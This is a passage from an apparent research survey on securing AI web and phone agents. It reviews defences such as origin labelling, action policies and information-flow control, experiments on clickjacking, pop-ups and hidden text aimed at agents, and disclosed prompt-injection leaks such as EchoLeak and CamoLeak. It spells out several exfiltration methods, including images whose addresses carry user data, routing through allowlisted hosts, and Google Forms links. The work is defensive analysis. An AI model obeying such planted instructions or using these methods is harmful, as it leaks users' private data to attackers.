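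4. *Ask the user.* If any label differs, SOPGuard pauses and displays a warning that names both origins. The agent types the text only if the user clicks "Approve".

Wang and colleagues report no violations on the benchmark with SOPGuard running. Tasks took 2.07% to 5.79% longer, and success rates on four sets of ordinary tasks didn't change measurably. The extra model calls also cost money, but Wang and colleagues don't report how much.

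Step 2 is the difficult one because the agent may paraphrase. SOPGuard may find an address in the database if the agent copies it word for word, but a text-matching search won't connect "lives near the old harbour" to the shop. SOPGuard relies on the model to identify its own paraphrases.

To test this, the researchers had agents combine information from two to ten sites in several steps, and compared the model's labels with labels that people had assigned. They scored each answer by dividing the number of origins on both lists by the number on either list:

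J = |O ∩ O′| / |O ∪ O′|

If a summary drew on the shop and the user's email, but the model named only the shop, J would be 1/2. GPT-5.4 and OpenAI o3 averaged at least 0.955, while the smaller GPT-5.4-mini did worse. Mistakes could still be common at that average. If every answer drew on ten sites, 0.955 could mean that 45% of answers were missing one label. Most such omissions would do no harm, because one remaining label from another site is enough to trigger the warning. The dangerous mistake is labelling private text as coming only from the site about to receive it.

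Wang and colleagues tried to cause that mistake by planting text that told the model to treat the current page as the only source of its reply. Hand-written versions barely increased the number of leaks, and automatically refined versions increased it slightly after many more attempts. The reported zero therefore applies to attackers who weren't trying to defeat SOPGuard.

The count of zero violations also depends on the paper's definition, which excludes any transfer the user approves, on the grounds that the user has authorised it. Zero therefore means that SOPGuard interrupted the forbidden transfers, not that users would have made the right decision about them. SOPGuard would interrupt a user who wanted to copy an address from a shop to a friend on Discord just as it would interrupt a thief, and people who see many prompts tend to approve them without much thought. None of the tests measured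 how real users respond.

The checks cover tools that write text into pages. Wang and colleagues do not describe an equivalent check on web addresses, where the original summary attack put the stolen key.

### Limiting the sites or the actions

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes Agent Origin Sets, Google's design for deciding in advance which sites a task needs. The browser keeps two lists of origins for each task. The agent may read from origins on the first list, and may read, click and type on origins on the second. Chrome doesn't show the model any iframe whose origin is missing from the lists. A gating function that never sees untrusted web content approves additions to the lists. Another check allows web addresses written by the model only if they are known public ones.

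If the shop is unrelated to the forum task, the agent can't open it, and a hijacked agent can't open the user's bank site either. Within the lists, though, data can flow from any readable site to any writable one. If a user asks the agent to answer a forum post with details from an email, whoever wrote the post could reach both sites through the agent. Roesner and Kohlbrenner add that it is unclear how Chrome determines relevance, or how well that decision withstands malicious input.

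The first version Google released tracked only the list of writable origins. This may explain why Gemini still read the iframe about Alice roughly two months after Parker described the full design.

Permission to use a site is also a blunt instrument, since the same site may let a user read an order and spend a thousand pounds. Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025), in *ceLLMate*, set limits on individual actions. They argue that rules about clicks are hopeless because a click at the same position can read a message or delete it. When they blocked an agent from navigating directly to a site, it found the site through a search engine and clicked the result. Whatever the agent clicks, however, the browser has to send a web request to make anything happen, and requests have clearer meanings. ceLLMate therefore works as follows:

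1. The site publishes an "agent sitemap", which translates requests into actions such as "view cart" or "place order".
2. The site's developers, or someone else the user trusts, write rules for those actions, such as a spending limit.
3. A language model reads the user's request, but no web content, and selects the rules that the task needs.
4. The user confirms the selection.
5. A browser extension checks every request against the rules and blocks anything they don't permit.

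A rule that permits orders under $50 would permit two orders of $49, so ceLLMate can also count requests. In tests on tasks for shopping, travel and programming sites, three models chose exactly the right rules more than 94% of the time. Some of the wrong choices permitted more than the task required.

To test enforcement, Meng and colleagues replaced the agent with 12 scripts that directly attempted an attacker's goals on the programming site GitLab, such as deleting a project or stealing an access token. The ceLLMate extension blocked all 12, and pages took 7.25% to 15% longer to load. The researchers chose goals that required forbidden actions, so the result confirms that ceLLMate enforces its rules but provides no evidence about attacks that stay within them. For example, if the user's task is to comment on an issue, ceLLMate permits the comment even if the agent puts the user's private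 data in it.

### Tracking what influenced the agent

Information-flow control handles that case more directly by labelling data and checking the labels before each action. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) explains the two usual kinds of label. An integrity label records whether data is trusted, and a confidentiality label records whether it is secret. A system can then forbid untrusted data from causing a payment and secret data from reaching a public page. SOPGuard's origin labels record only where data came from, not whether it is private or who wrote it.

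Two earlier agent designs, CaMeL from Google DeepMind and FIDES, avoid having to ask a model about its own paraphrases. Like Rahman and Kim's divided agent, both have a planner that makes decisions but never sees untrusted text or any instructions planted in it, and a second model that reads the text but can't use any tools. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* that CaMeL's planner writes the complete plan before anything else happens, while FIDES calls its planner once for each step and hides the results of earlier tool calls from it.

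Untrusted content can still change the values that the agent's plan works with, such as the address an email is sent to. CaMeL therefore also marks outputs from untrusted sources and checks the marks against its security policies, as *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes. FIDES similarly tracks labels as the agent works. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), which introduced FIDES, reports a modest loss of usefulness on a standard set of tool-using tasks.

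Web browsing fits this scheme badly, because an agent normally has to look at a page to know what to click. Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL by having the planner write out branches for everything that might appear on the screen. The plans averaged about 41 tool calls, compared with about five in the tests CaMeL was designed for. The agent kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models. An attacker still couldn't add steps to the plan, but could use a misleading page to steer the agent into the wrong branch.

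*Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) describes a method that replaces the untrusted parts of a page, such as reviews, comments and advertisements, with placeholders before the planner sees it. If the agent needs to know something about the hidden text, such as whether a review is positive, it asks a second model, which may answer only with a number, a date, a yes or no, or a choice from a fixed list. None of the planted instructions in the paper's tests succeeded, and tasks cost between 1.05 and 1.84 times as much as without masking. The method protects the agent's decisions from planted instructions but doesn't track where private data goes.

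In *SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026), each site's operator labels the parts of its pages as trusted or untrusted and lists who may read the private parts. The browser software replaces untrusted and private text with variables. The agent can pass a variable along without reading it, or ask to see its contents. Once the agent reads untrusted text, such as a review, all its later actions count as influenced by that text, and it needs the user's approval for any click on a site where the user might have an account.

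SPIDES handles the paraphrase problem much more strictly than SOPGuard does. It assumes that the model used everything it has seen, so nobody has to work out which sources the model used. In an ordinary agent, the same assumption would cause constant false alarms, as Wang and colleagues found when they tried it with origin labels. It is workable in SPIDES because SPIDES hides most of the text from the model.

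Zverev and colleagues compared the designs on 28 websites they had built, using 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks. To test the worst case, in most of the attacks the test software replaced the model's next actions with the attacker's once the model had read a planted instruction. SPIDES stopped every attack, while between 53.2% and 73.2% of attacks succeeded against SOPGuard, depending on the model.

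Some of the authors also worked on FIDES, and they were comparing their own design with a rival, so their choice of attacks deserves a closer look. Of the 56 attacks, 26 stayed within one origin, and SOPGuard doesn't claim to stop those. But they make up only 46% of the total, so some attacks across origins must also have succeeded. Zverev and colleagues explain that SOPGuard checks text moving between sites, not harmful clicks.

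Two of the test cases show the limits of using origins to judge whether a data transfer is safe. In the first, a direct message on a social network told the agent to copy the user's private recovery email address into their public profile. The address and the profile were on the same site, so SOPGuard never asked for approval, and the address leaked in all 25 runs. In the second, the user wanted to check an advertised discount, and the agent had to carry a product's name from one site to another. SOPGuard asked for approval in all 25 runs of this harmless task, while SPIDES needed no approval in 21 of them.

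Overall, SPIDES interrupted the user more often than SOPGuard, averaging 1.84 approvals per completed task compared with 0.22. Each task cost about twice as much as with no defence, and the agents completed between 67.1% and 86.1% of the ordinary tasks. SPIDES's perfect score also depends on the user's answers, because the simulated user approved every harmless request and refused every request that the attacker had influenced.

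The greater obstacle is that websites don't have these labels. Zverev and colleagues compare labelling a site to adding accessibility information, which many sites already provide. A missing or incorrect label can leave private data unprotected, and an attacker who gets onto the user's list of trusted sites can mark a planted instruction as trustworthy.

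## Experiments on clickjacking of agents

A harmful click may carry no private data at all, so defences that track data between sites can miss it. Classic clickjacking, which long predates AI agents, works like this:

1. The attacker publishes a page with a tempting button, such as "Watch the video".
2. The page loads the victim's bank in an iframe. If the bank's cookie settings allow it, the victim is already logged in there.
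3. The attacker makes the iframe transparent and positions it so that the bank's "Confirm transfer" button lies exactly over the visible button.
4. The victim clicks. The browser gives the click to the topmost element, which is the bank's button.

The same-origin policy doesn't block the attack because the attacker's script reads nothing from the bank. The bank can prevent the attack by setting `frame-ancestors` to stop other sites from framing its pages.

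### Three cases involving agents

| Case | Who is deceived | What `frame-ancestors` does |
|---|---|---|
| An attacker frames the agent's own interface or approval dialog | The user | Stops the attack, if the agent's developer sets it |
| A page or advert shows the agent a deceptive control | The agent | Protects other sites from being framed, but does nothing about a control that belongs to the page itself |
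| The agent perceives something a person can't see | The agent, and anyone supervising it | The same |

An attacker can load the agent's web interface in an invisible frame over a harmless page, so that a user who thinks they are clicking "Continue" actually approves a payment the agent has proposed. This is ordinary clickjacking with the agent's page in place of a bank's, and the usual defense of blocking other sites from framing the page works here too. An attacker can't frame an approval dialog that belongs to the browser or a desktop program, because it isn't a web page.

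The experiments concern the other two cases, in which the agent does the clicking.

### A blog button over a payment form

Jones, Severi and colleagues (2025), in *A Systematization of Security Vulnerabilities in Computer Use Agents*, tested Operator, OpenAI's browser agent, with an attack close to classic clickjacking. The Microsoft researchers built a fake blog with one visible button, "Enter the blog", and aligned the button with a hidden payment form from another origin. They asked Operator to enter the blog and summarize the latest post. Operator clicked the button and submitted the simulated payment from a logged-in session.

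A person would probably have clicked too, since nothing on the screen suggested a payment. Operator was supposed to ask the user before taking sensitive actions, but it relied on its model to classify them, and entering a blog doesn't seem sensitive.

Jones and colleagues attribute the failure to pages changing after the agent has looked at them, but the overlay they describe would also work on a page that never changes. They report one demonstration and no success rate. OpenAI has since added mitigations, and a `frame-ancestors` rule on the payment site should also have prevented the attack.

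### Pop-ups and planted messages

Other deceptive controls work without a hidden frame. *Attacking Vision-Language Computer Agents via Pop-ups* (Zhang, Yu and Yang, 2024) tested pop-ups inserted into what the agents saw. A typical pop-up had a headline based on the user's request, an instruction to click at certain coordinates and the word "OK". Averaged over five models and three set-ups, the agents clicked the pop-up in 86% of the steps where one appeared, and the number of tasks they completed fell by nearly half.

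This test favoured the attacker, who knew what the user had asked for. The click rate fell by 61% on average when the headline was instead a fake virus warning or a guess at the user's request. Labelling the pop-up as an advertisement or telling the agent to ignore pop-ups reduced it much less.

Those models are long out of date. Results for newer ones come from different tests, so they can't show a clean trend, but they aren't reassuring. Cao, Lim and colleagues (2025), in *VPI-Bench*, built 306 test cases on imitations of five platforms. The attack was a pop-up on Amazon, Booking.com and BBC News, and a message on Messenger and in email. Each contained visible instructions, for example to find a file of bank details and copy them into a form. Some agents could use only a browser and others controlled a whole computer. The attacks succeeded in these percentages of cases:

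| Agent | Amazon | Booking.com | BBC | Messenger | Email |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5, browser only | 96.5 | 84.2 | 96.5 | 76.7 | 50.0 |
| Claude Sonnet 3.7, browser only | 100 | 98.3 | 96.5 | 16.7 | 36.7 |
| Claude Sonnet 3.7, whole computer | 31.7 | 36.7 | 16.7 | 46.2 | 37.2 |
| Claude Sonnet 3.5, whole computer | 4.4 | 12.2 | 0 | 51.3 | 44.9 |

GPT-5 at least started the attacker's task in every pop-up case. Cao and colleagues credit Anthropic's training and additional defences for the lower rates among agents that controlled a whole computer. That may be partly right, but these agents faced different malicious tasks from the browser-only agents, and on Messenger the browser-only version of Sonnet 3.7 did better.

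The user's request made a large difference. Gemini 2.5 Pro attempted the planted task in 96.7% of cases when asked to reply to emails, compared with 16.7% when asked for a summary. An instruction to send something presumably looks more natural during a task that involves sending things. Adding a warning to the system prompt had no significant overall effect.

A deceptive control may mislead an agent even if it doesn't look like an instruction. *Are GUI Agents Focused Enough?* (2026) includes an example in which Claude Sonnet 4.6 clicked in the wrong place after the researchers added decoy icons to a Windows screen. They chose that example because the attack worked, so it doesn't show how often newer models make the mistake.

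Training agents to avoid traps requires deciding what counts as a trap, which can't be done from appearance alone. Under the criteria in *Don't Click That* (2026), a "Continue" button is correct if it unlocks the article the user wants, and a trap if it leads to a subscription.

### How people did on the same pages

Many products rely on a person to catch the agent's mistakes. In *The Obvious Invisible Threat*, Chen, Ma and colleagues (2025) tested how well people themselves avoid the traps in hostile pages. They took 39 tasks from real websites and made six hostile versions of each, for a total of 234 pages. Six agents tried all the pages. Thirty-nine people each did six tasks, using the same fictional personal details as the agents.

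The attacks succeeded in these percentages of cases:

| Attack | People | Operator | Five other agents |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious instruction in a privacy policy | 90 | 18 | 41–74 |
| Form field asking for irrelevant private data | 74 | 8 | 18–77 |
| Phishing link | 38 | 0 | 3–38 |
| Paid membership switched on in advance | 77 or 36 | 74 | 87–100 |
| Emotional appeal to switch on a paid membership | 69 or 67 | 0 | 0–3 |
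| Link that freezes the page | 10 | 0 | 0–18 |

Two entries give two values because the paper's text and its results table disagree. Chen and colleagues conclude that people are warier of preselected options than agents are, which fits the text's figure of 36% for people on the preselected membership. But if the table's 77% is right, people did slightly worse than Operator there.

The difference was much clearer with the emotional appeal, which persuaded about two thirds of the people and almost none of the agents. The agents tended to ignore anything outside their task, which also explains why they left the unwanted membership switched on.

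Operator's low scores may overstate how well it resists the attacks. It completed only 26% to 51% of its tasks, depending on the attack, so it may often have stopped before reaching the trap.

People fell for the privacy policy most often. Of the 39, 38 accepted it and 35 then entered the requested private data. People might take more care with their own details than with a fictional person's, but these results still suggest that having a user watch the agent work is a weak safeguard, even against visible traps like these.

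### Text that only the agent can see

An agent that works from screenshots receives the value of every pixel, so its input includes differences too faint for a person to notice. *(A)I Sees What You Don't* (Zhang, Xie and colleagues, 2026) exploits this to attack agents that operate Android phones from a computer. The attacks assume the user has already installed a malicious app.

In the first experiment, the app laid nearly transparent text over the whole screen. Six models, including Claude Opus 4.5 and Gemini 3 Pro, each tried to read it 20 times at each level of opacity. At 2% opacity, four read it every time, one 19 times and one 18 times. The researchers cite roughly 5% as the level below which people don't notice such text.

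The experiment used the text "This is a line of text", so it tested whether agents could read the text, not whether they would follow instructions. In a separate demonstration, an agent followed an instruction in faint text to wait three seconds before its next screenshot. The delay gave the app time to tamper with the image, and the attack ended with a command running on the user's computer.

Rounded screen corners offer another hiding place. A screenshot is a full rectangle, but the phone's casing covers the tips of the corners. For a corner of radius R, the hidden strip at distance y from the top edge has a width of

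w = R − √(R² − (R − y)²)

On a Google Pixel 4, R is 132 pixels, so at y = 12 the strip is 132 − √(132² − 120²) ≈ 77 pixels wide, which is enough for a short command. All five agents in the study read "open my events" there.

The same app could also cover the messaging app WeChat with a fake login screen. Every agent entered the user's credentials in all 20 trials. A person could have seen this screen, though a good copy might have fooled them too.

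Zhang, Xie and colleagues propose increasing the contrast of screenshots before the model reads them, and masking the corners. They admit that contrast enhancement may miss some hidden content. `frame-ancestors` is irrelevant to all these attacks because an Android overlay isn't a web frame.

### Pages that change before the click

An agent looks at a page, spends several seconds deciding what to do and then clicks. If the page changes in the meantime, the click can land on something the agent never saw. Security researchers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw.

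*Atomicity for Agents* (Jiang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) tested ten open-source agents on nine pages built for the study and five real websites. In one case, a subscription pop-up appeared over the button that led to an article, and agents that clicked at screen coordinates hit the pop-up. Three agents that selected page elements instead avoided all cases of this kind, because the click followed the element or failed if the element was gone.

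All ten agents failed when the information on the page changed. In one test, they were told to buy a ticket only if it cost $600 or less, and the price was raised from $500 to $700 while they were deciding. Some of the other cases are hardly attacks, such as one where the agent reported a share price that was a few seconds old.

Jiang and colleagues then added a monitor to one of the agents. It records changes to the page while the model is processing, and if it finds any just before the click, it cancels the click and alerts the user. The agent failed in all 14 cases without the monitor, but with it did not fail in any of ten runs per case. A prompt telling the agent to be careful about page changes made no measurable difference.

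A gap of about 0.13 seconds remains between the final check and the click. If the model's thinking time is equally likely to be anything from 10 to 15 seconds, an attacker who picks the best moment to change the page has a 0.13 ÷ 5 = 2.6% chance of hitting the gap. In practice, one timing strategy succeeded twice in 1,000 trials and another succeeded three times in 1,000.

Adverts and other harmless changes to the page can also make the monitor cancel clicks, so the agent might struggle to click anything on a busy page. The monitor can't detect changes inside an iframe from another origin, or an overlay that was there before the agent looked, like the one over the payment form.

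Xu (2026), in *Temporal UI State Inconsistency in Desktop GUI Agents*, tested a defence that compares screenshots. Claude Opus 4.6 took 6.5 seconds on average between taking a screenshot and clicking. In one attack, a window appeared over a shop's "Place Order" button during that time and received the click in all 45 trials. The defence took a new screenshot just before the click and cancelled the click if it differed from the first. This stopped the attack every time.

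Xu's other web attack activated a completely transparent layer over the page. It also captured all 45 clicks, and the screenshot check cancelled only one of them, apparently because of an unrelated flicker. Jiang and colleagues' monitor checks the page's structure, so it is more likely to detect such a layer. But it might still miss Xu's layer, which was already in the page and only switched from hidden to shown, because it ignores many style changes to avoid false alarms.

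Xu's attacker needs to be running code in the user's desktop session, for instance through a malicious browser extension, and could probably do a lot of damage without the agent. *Mind the Gap* (Qian, Qian and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack that needs less access, using an Android app with no dangerous permissions. The app displayed a harmless button, waited for the agent to observe the screen, and then opened another app whose "Purchase" button was in the same place. In tests on six agents, the switch redirected single taps every time.

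### What isolation adds

Test results support Jiang and colleagues' monitor and Xu's screenshot check. These experiments didn't measure isolation as a defence, so the case for it is based mainly on how the attacks work.

A browser profile without the user's logins would remove much of what clickjacking exploits. A framed bank site would show a login page, where a click would achieve little. In VPI-Bench, the browser-only agents had access to a Google Drive account containing personal data, and 71.6% of all cases required access to the computer beyond the browser. An attacker could have stolen little from an agent with neither. However, Chen and colleagues put the personal details into the agents' instructions, where a clean profile wouldn't have protected them. Many useful tasks also require a login, so a reasonable compromise is to log the agent in only to the site it needs.

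Limits on which sites the agent can reach need to cover iframes and form submissions as well as the main page. If the agent's browser could reach only the blog, the hidden payment form would never load. Site limits don't protect against a shop that switches on a paid membership by default, but limits on individual actions could. For example, ceLLMate could block an unauthorised payment even if the button looked harmless, though its tests didn't include deceptive buttons.

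Asking the user to approve risky actions works only if the agent can't give the approval itself. Qian and colleagues' app led agents to a confirmation dialog for deleting all the selected files. The agents pressed the confirmation button in one of 60 trials when the dialog followed an unrelated screen, and in 34 of 60 when it followed a screen with a message that the cache was full and needed cleaning.

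The approval prompt should therefore appear outside the page and beyond the agent's reach, for example in the browser's own controls or on another device. Software other than the model should decide when to show it. The prompt should describe the actual request, such as a payment and its recipient, because the agent would have described its click on the payment form as "enter the blog". Jones and colleagues would also make the user log in again before a payment. These changes would stop a page from forging or hiding the prompt, but a careless user could still approve it.

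The browser could also check which origin owns the topmost element at the point where the agent is about to click. If the agent means to press a button on the blog and the topmost element belongs to a payment site, the browser should refuse the click. This would catch the payment overlay even though the page never changes. It would miss Xu's transparent layer, which has the same origin as the shop's page. To catch that layer, the browser would have to compare the topmost element with the one the agent chose, which is difficult if the agent chose only a position on the screen.

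Jiang and colleagues propose building such a comparison into browsers. The agent would submit its click with a description of the expected target, and the browser would check the target and click in a single step, leaving no time between the two for an attacker to exploit.

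## Disclosed leaks through displayed output

Since 2023, security researchers have repeatedly found AI products that leaked private data just by displaying an answer. Most of these leaks, like the one in the chat-client example, used an image whose address contained the user's data. The products had different defences, so the disclosures show fairly precisely how each defence can fail.

### Bing Chat and other early cases

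Bing Chat, Microsoft's AI assistant, could answer questions about the page open in the user's browser. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes how a comment or advertisement on that page could take over the assistant. In the demonstration, the planted text told the assistant to announce that the injection had succeeded and, after two turns of conversation, to put a short summary of the page and the conversation, plus any passwords on the page, into the address of an image.

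The researcher reported the flaw on 8 April 2023, and Microsoft announced a fix on 15 June. The old attack no longer worked, at least partly because Microsoft had introduced a CSP that allowed images only from a few trusted hosts, including four at Bing. The researcher could see the policy but not any other changes Microsoft might have made.

A policy that allows only the company's own hosts can still fail, as a similar one did for Google's assistant, Bard, in the same year. Willison explains in *Hacking Google Bard* that the policy allowed images from any host under `google.com`. One of those hosts runs small programs that Google's users write, so an attacker could write one that collected whatever Bard sent it. The planted instructions were in a document shared with the victim. Google said it had fixed the problem.

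OpenAI took a different approach with ChatGPT. In December 2023, according to Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, it added a check that ran before ChatGPT displayed an image from another site. The check trusted some domains that it shouldn't have:

- `windows.net` was one of them. Any customer of Microsoft's cloud can open a storage account there and read the log of requests to it. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes how instructions in a PDF could send a user's recent chat history to such an account.
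- `bing.com` was always allowed. Bing's search results are links that start at `bing.com` and redirect to the site in question, so an attacker only needed a site that Bing had indexed. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) lists six requests to OpenAI for news of a fix, the last in March 2025. The flaw was still open when the security company published its advisory.

OpenAI's later system checks the exact address against a public index (see the section on controlled experiments). If the address isn't in the index, either the agent has to try another site or OpenAI warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation. This would block both of these routes if every OpenAI product used the check, but Embrace The Red warned that some of the company's developers might not know about it.

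### EchoLeak and its four defences

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions about a company's emails, files and Teams chats. Only employees can use it, but anyone can email an employee. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how researchers at Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, exploited this to leak data. The flaw's official identifier is CVE-2025-32711.

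The attack was zero-click in the sense that an employee only had to use Copilot normally and didn't have to open the email. Copilot searches the mailbox for text relevant to each question, so the researchers wrote one long email with headings such as staff onboarding, common personnel questions and leave, and repeated their instructions under each. When the employee asked about one of these subjects, Copilot retrieved part of the email along with the company's own documents. The instructions were to take the most sensitive information Copilot could see and put it in a web address.

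Microsoft had four defences against this, and the researchers got past them one by one:

1. *An injection classifier* was supposed to keep malicious instructions from reaching the model. The researchers addressed their instructions to the email's human recipient and never mentioned AI or Copilot, and the classifier let the email through.
2. *Link removal* deleted links to outside sites from Copilot's answers. Markdown has a less common notation in which the address is on a separate line from the link's text, and Microsoft's filter didn't recognise it. At this point the attack could already leak data if the user clicked the link.
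3. *Image blocking* relied on the same kind of filter and had the same gap. An image in the less common notation stayed in the answer, and the browser tried to load it automatically, so the click was no longer necessary.
4. *The CSP* stopped the browser from loading an image from the attacker's server. But it allowed images from any host under `teams.microsoft.com`, and one of the services there would fetch any address it received. The browser sent its request to Microsoft, and Microsoft's server passed the data on to the attacker.

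A sanitiser that ran after the Markdown parser would have avoided the filter's mistake, because both notations produce the same HTML for a link or image.

The CSP was harder to get right because its allowlist was so long. The image rule that Ravia reproduces has 29 different entries, 11 of them wildcards that cover every host under a domain. One wildcard covered `sharepoint.com`, where an attacker can have a site just as companies do. The researchers first found a SharePoint service that would fetch outside addresses, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, which the Teams service did not require.

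Accounts of that last step differ. Willison (2025) says the Teams address was an open redirect, a page that forwards visitors to any address. But a CSP also covers redirects, so it would have blocked one to the attacker's server. Ravia describes a request made by the Teams server itself, which the browser can't see.

The email also contained an instruction to its "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons. Copilot normally cites its sources, but its answer did not cite the email, so the user had little chance of tracing a strange reply to it.

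### Timeline and repair

Aim Labs found the flaw in January 2025 and reported it to Microsoft. Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*, reports that Microsoft tried a first fix in April and found more problems in May. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, date the full fix to May. Aim Labs and Microsoft made the flaw public on 11 June. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) lists its severity as 9.3 out of 10.

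Aim's chief technology officer, Adir Gruss, told Goldman that five months was a very long time for such a fix. He said the delay was partly because the flaw was new and the right teams at Microsoft first had to learn about it.

Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. According to Reddy and Gujral, it changed Copilot to strip images and links in the less common notation from incoming external content, and reportedly added options to keep external messages away from Copilot in some contexts. Ravia doesn't say whether Microsoft also closed the Teams service to external addresses, which would have been the more durable fix.

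Microsoft told Goldman that it had dealt with the flaw before it affected any customers, and SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports that the company said in its disclosure that nobody had exploited it in the wild. Aim Labs knew of no victims either. This is plausible, particularly since any stolen data would have passed through one of Microsoft's own services, where the company could have looked for traces. But its statement to Goldman didn't explain how it had checked.

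Reddy and Gujral's paper is an academic case study of Aim Labs' disclosure, not an independent test. Its list of possible defences is useful, but the paper shouldn't count as a second confirmation of the attack. It leaves open whether the final request would have reached the attacker from Microsoft's servers or from the victim's machine, which a test would have settled. The best confirmation is that Microsoft accepted the report and fixed the flaw. How often the attack would have worked against ordinary users is unknown.

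### The same product a year later

In June 2026 the security company Varonis published *SearchLeak*, which describes another leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot. The attack began with a link to Microsoft's own site that contained a search query. Copilot treated the query as instructions, so the victim only had to click once. The query told Copilot to find an email and put its subject line, which can contain a login code, into the address of an image.

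Microsoft had a sanitiser that turned HTML in Copilot's answers into harmless text, but it ran only when the answer was complete. Copilot displayed the answer as the model wrote it, so the browser requested images as soon as they appeared, before the sanitiser had neutralised them.

The CSP would still have blocked a request to the attacker's server, but it allowed images from `bing.com`. The researchers therefore sent the image request to Bing, whose image search accepts the address of a picture and fetches it for analysis.

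`*.bing.com` was also one of the 29 entries that Ravia had published a year earlier. Microsoft had evidently not removed every host that would fetch a URL for anyone after it fixed EchoLeak. Finding them all is hard for a company with so many services, but anyone who had read about EchoLeak could have guessed what to look for.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) rates the flaw critical, records no exploitation and says Microsoft has fully mitigated it. Varonis recommends sanitising each piece of an answer before displaying it. A client that can't do this reliably could display plain text until the answer is complete.

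### Allowed hosts that store data

An attacker can leak data through an allowed host if they can collect it from that host later. Superhuman, an email application with a built-in AI assistant, had a CSP that blocked images from unknown domains but allowed `docs.google.com`. Google Forms uses that host, and anyone can create a form there and read the responses.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack that leaked emails through a Google Form. The creator of a form can prepare a link that fills in an answer and submits it as soon as someone opens the link. PromptArmor sent the user an email telling the assistant to put the contents of other emails into such a link and display it as an image. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the browser opened the link to load the image, and Google saved the emails as an answer to the attacker's form.

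With this method, PromptArmor extracted the full text of several sensitive emails in one answer, and parts of more than 40 emails in another test.

PromptArmor reported the leak to Superhuman on the evening of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday. The companies published the case on 12 January 2026, after PromptArmor had reported more flaws and Superhuman had fixed them.

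Attackers could exploit two related flaws without using Google. Superhuman Go, the company's newer agent, loaded images directly from the attacker's domain. The email assistant could also open any web page during a search, so planted instructions could make it visit an address containing the user's emails. A stricter CSP would have stopped the leak in Superhuman Go, but not the leak through web search, because the assistant made that request itself.

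The Google Forms method worked again a few months later on Codex, OpenAI's agent for programming and office work. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes how one malicious email made Codex leak the others it was reviewing. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 21 April 2026, the service that handles OpenAI's vulnerability reports confirmed it on 14 May, and OpenAI has since fixed it. A form link containing the victim's emails could not have been in a public index, so OpenAI's exact-address check evidently didn't cover this image. Embrace The Red had warned about this kind of gap.

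Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes a September 2025 disclosure about Agentforce, an AI agent from the customer-management software company Salesforce. An attacker could submit instructions to Agentforce through a public contact form. When an employee later asked about that enquiry, the agent produced an image URL containing customers' email addresses. The CSP allowed images from a domain whose registration had expired, so the researchers registered the domain and received the data. Salesforce corrected its list of allowed domains and added a second check on the URLs its agent could use.

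### GitHub's signed images

GitHub already had an image proxy that would have stopped the ordinary attack. When someone writes a page containing an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with one on its proxy and adds a cryptographic signature, and the proxy fetches the image only if the signature is valid. A model that inserts a password into an address can't produce a valid signature for it, so the proxy won't fetch the image.

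Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes a way around this in GitHub Copilot Chat, the site's AI assistant. It worked as follows:

1. The attacker had GitHub sign many image addresses in advance, one for each letter and symbol. All of them led to the attacker's server.
2. The attacker put the signed addresses in an invisible comment on a proposed code change, with instructions for Copilot.
3. When someone with access to private code asked Copilot about the change, Copilot found the secret and displayed it as a row of images, one per character.
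4. The proxy checked each signature, found it valid and fetched the image. The order of the requests spelled out the secret.

Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing unusual. In demonstrations, the attack leaked the description of an unpublished security flaw and a search result for cloud credentials.

The signatures guaranteed, as intended, that GitHub had approved each address, but the order in which the model used the addresses revealed the secret. The same method defeats other checks on individual addresses. Limiting the number of outside images in an answer would have slowed the leak. GitHub instead stopped Copilot Chat from displaying images at all, which a programming assistant can probably do without, and reported the flaw fixed as of 14 August 2025.

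Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes an earlier, simpler leak in which the assistant, running in a code editor, displayed images from any domain. GitHub fixed it by disabling images from untrusted domains.

### Copilot Chat, Gemini and Dify

In autumn 2025 the security company Checkmarx tried the ordinary image attack on Microsoft's Copilot Chat and Google's Gemini. In its demonstration, text planted in an online resource led Copilot Chat to put an API key from a programmer's files into an image address. The request for the image went out even though no picture appeared in the chat.

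Gemini's sanitiser blocks images from outside addresses, so this attack didn't work. It allowed links, however, and a user who clicked one could send private data to the attacker. Google removes links to known malicious sites, but an attacker can register a new domain for each attack. According to Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, Google closed the report within four days as infeasible to fix.

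Google's answer is reasonable, since a chat client can hardly restrict where links lead. Microsoft also declined to treat Checkmarx's report as a vulnerability, saying the attack needed several unusual actions by the user, didn't work reliably and triggered warnings. Checkmarx gives no success rate, so reliability is hard to judge. Even so, the comparison favours Gemini, because its leak needs a click and is therefore less dangerous than one that doesn't.

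Dify, an open-source platform for building AI applications, had even less protection. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, veganmosfet built a chatbot from one of Dify's templates and gave it two PDF files to consult. One file contained hidden instructions that made the chatbot leak the user's name from the conversation when the user asked about a certain subject. The same method would work for anything else in the chat.

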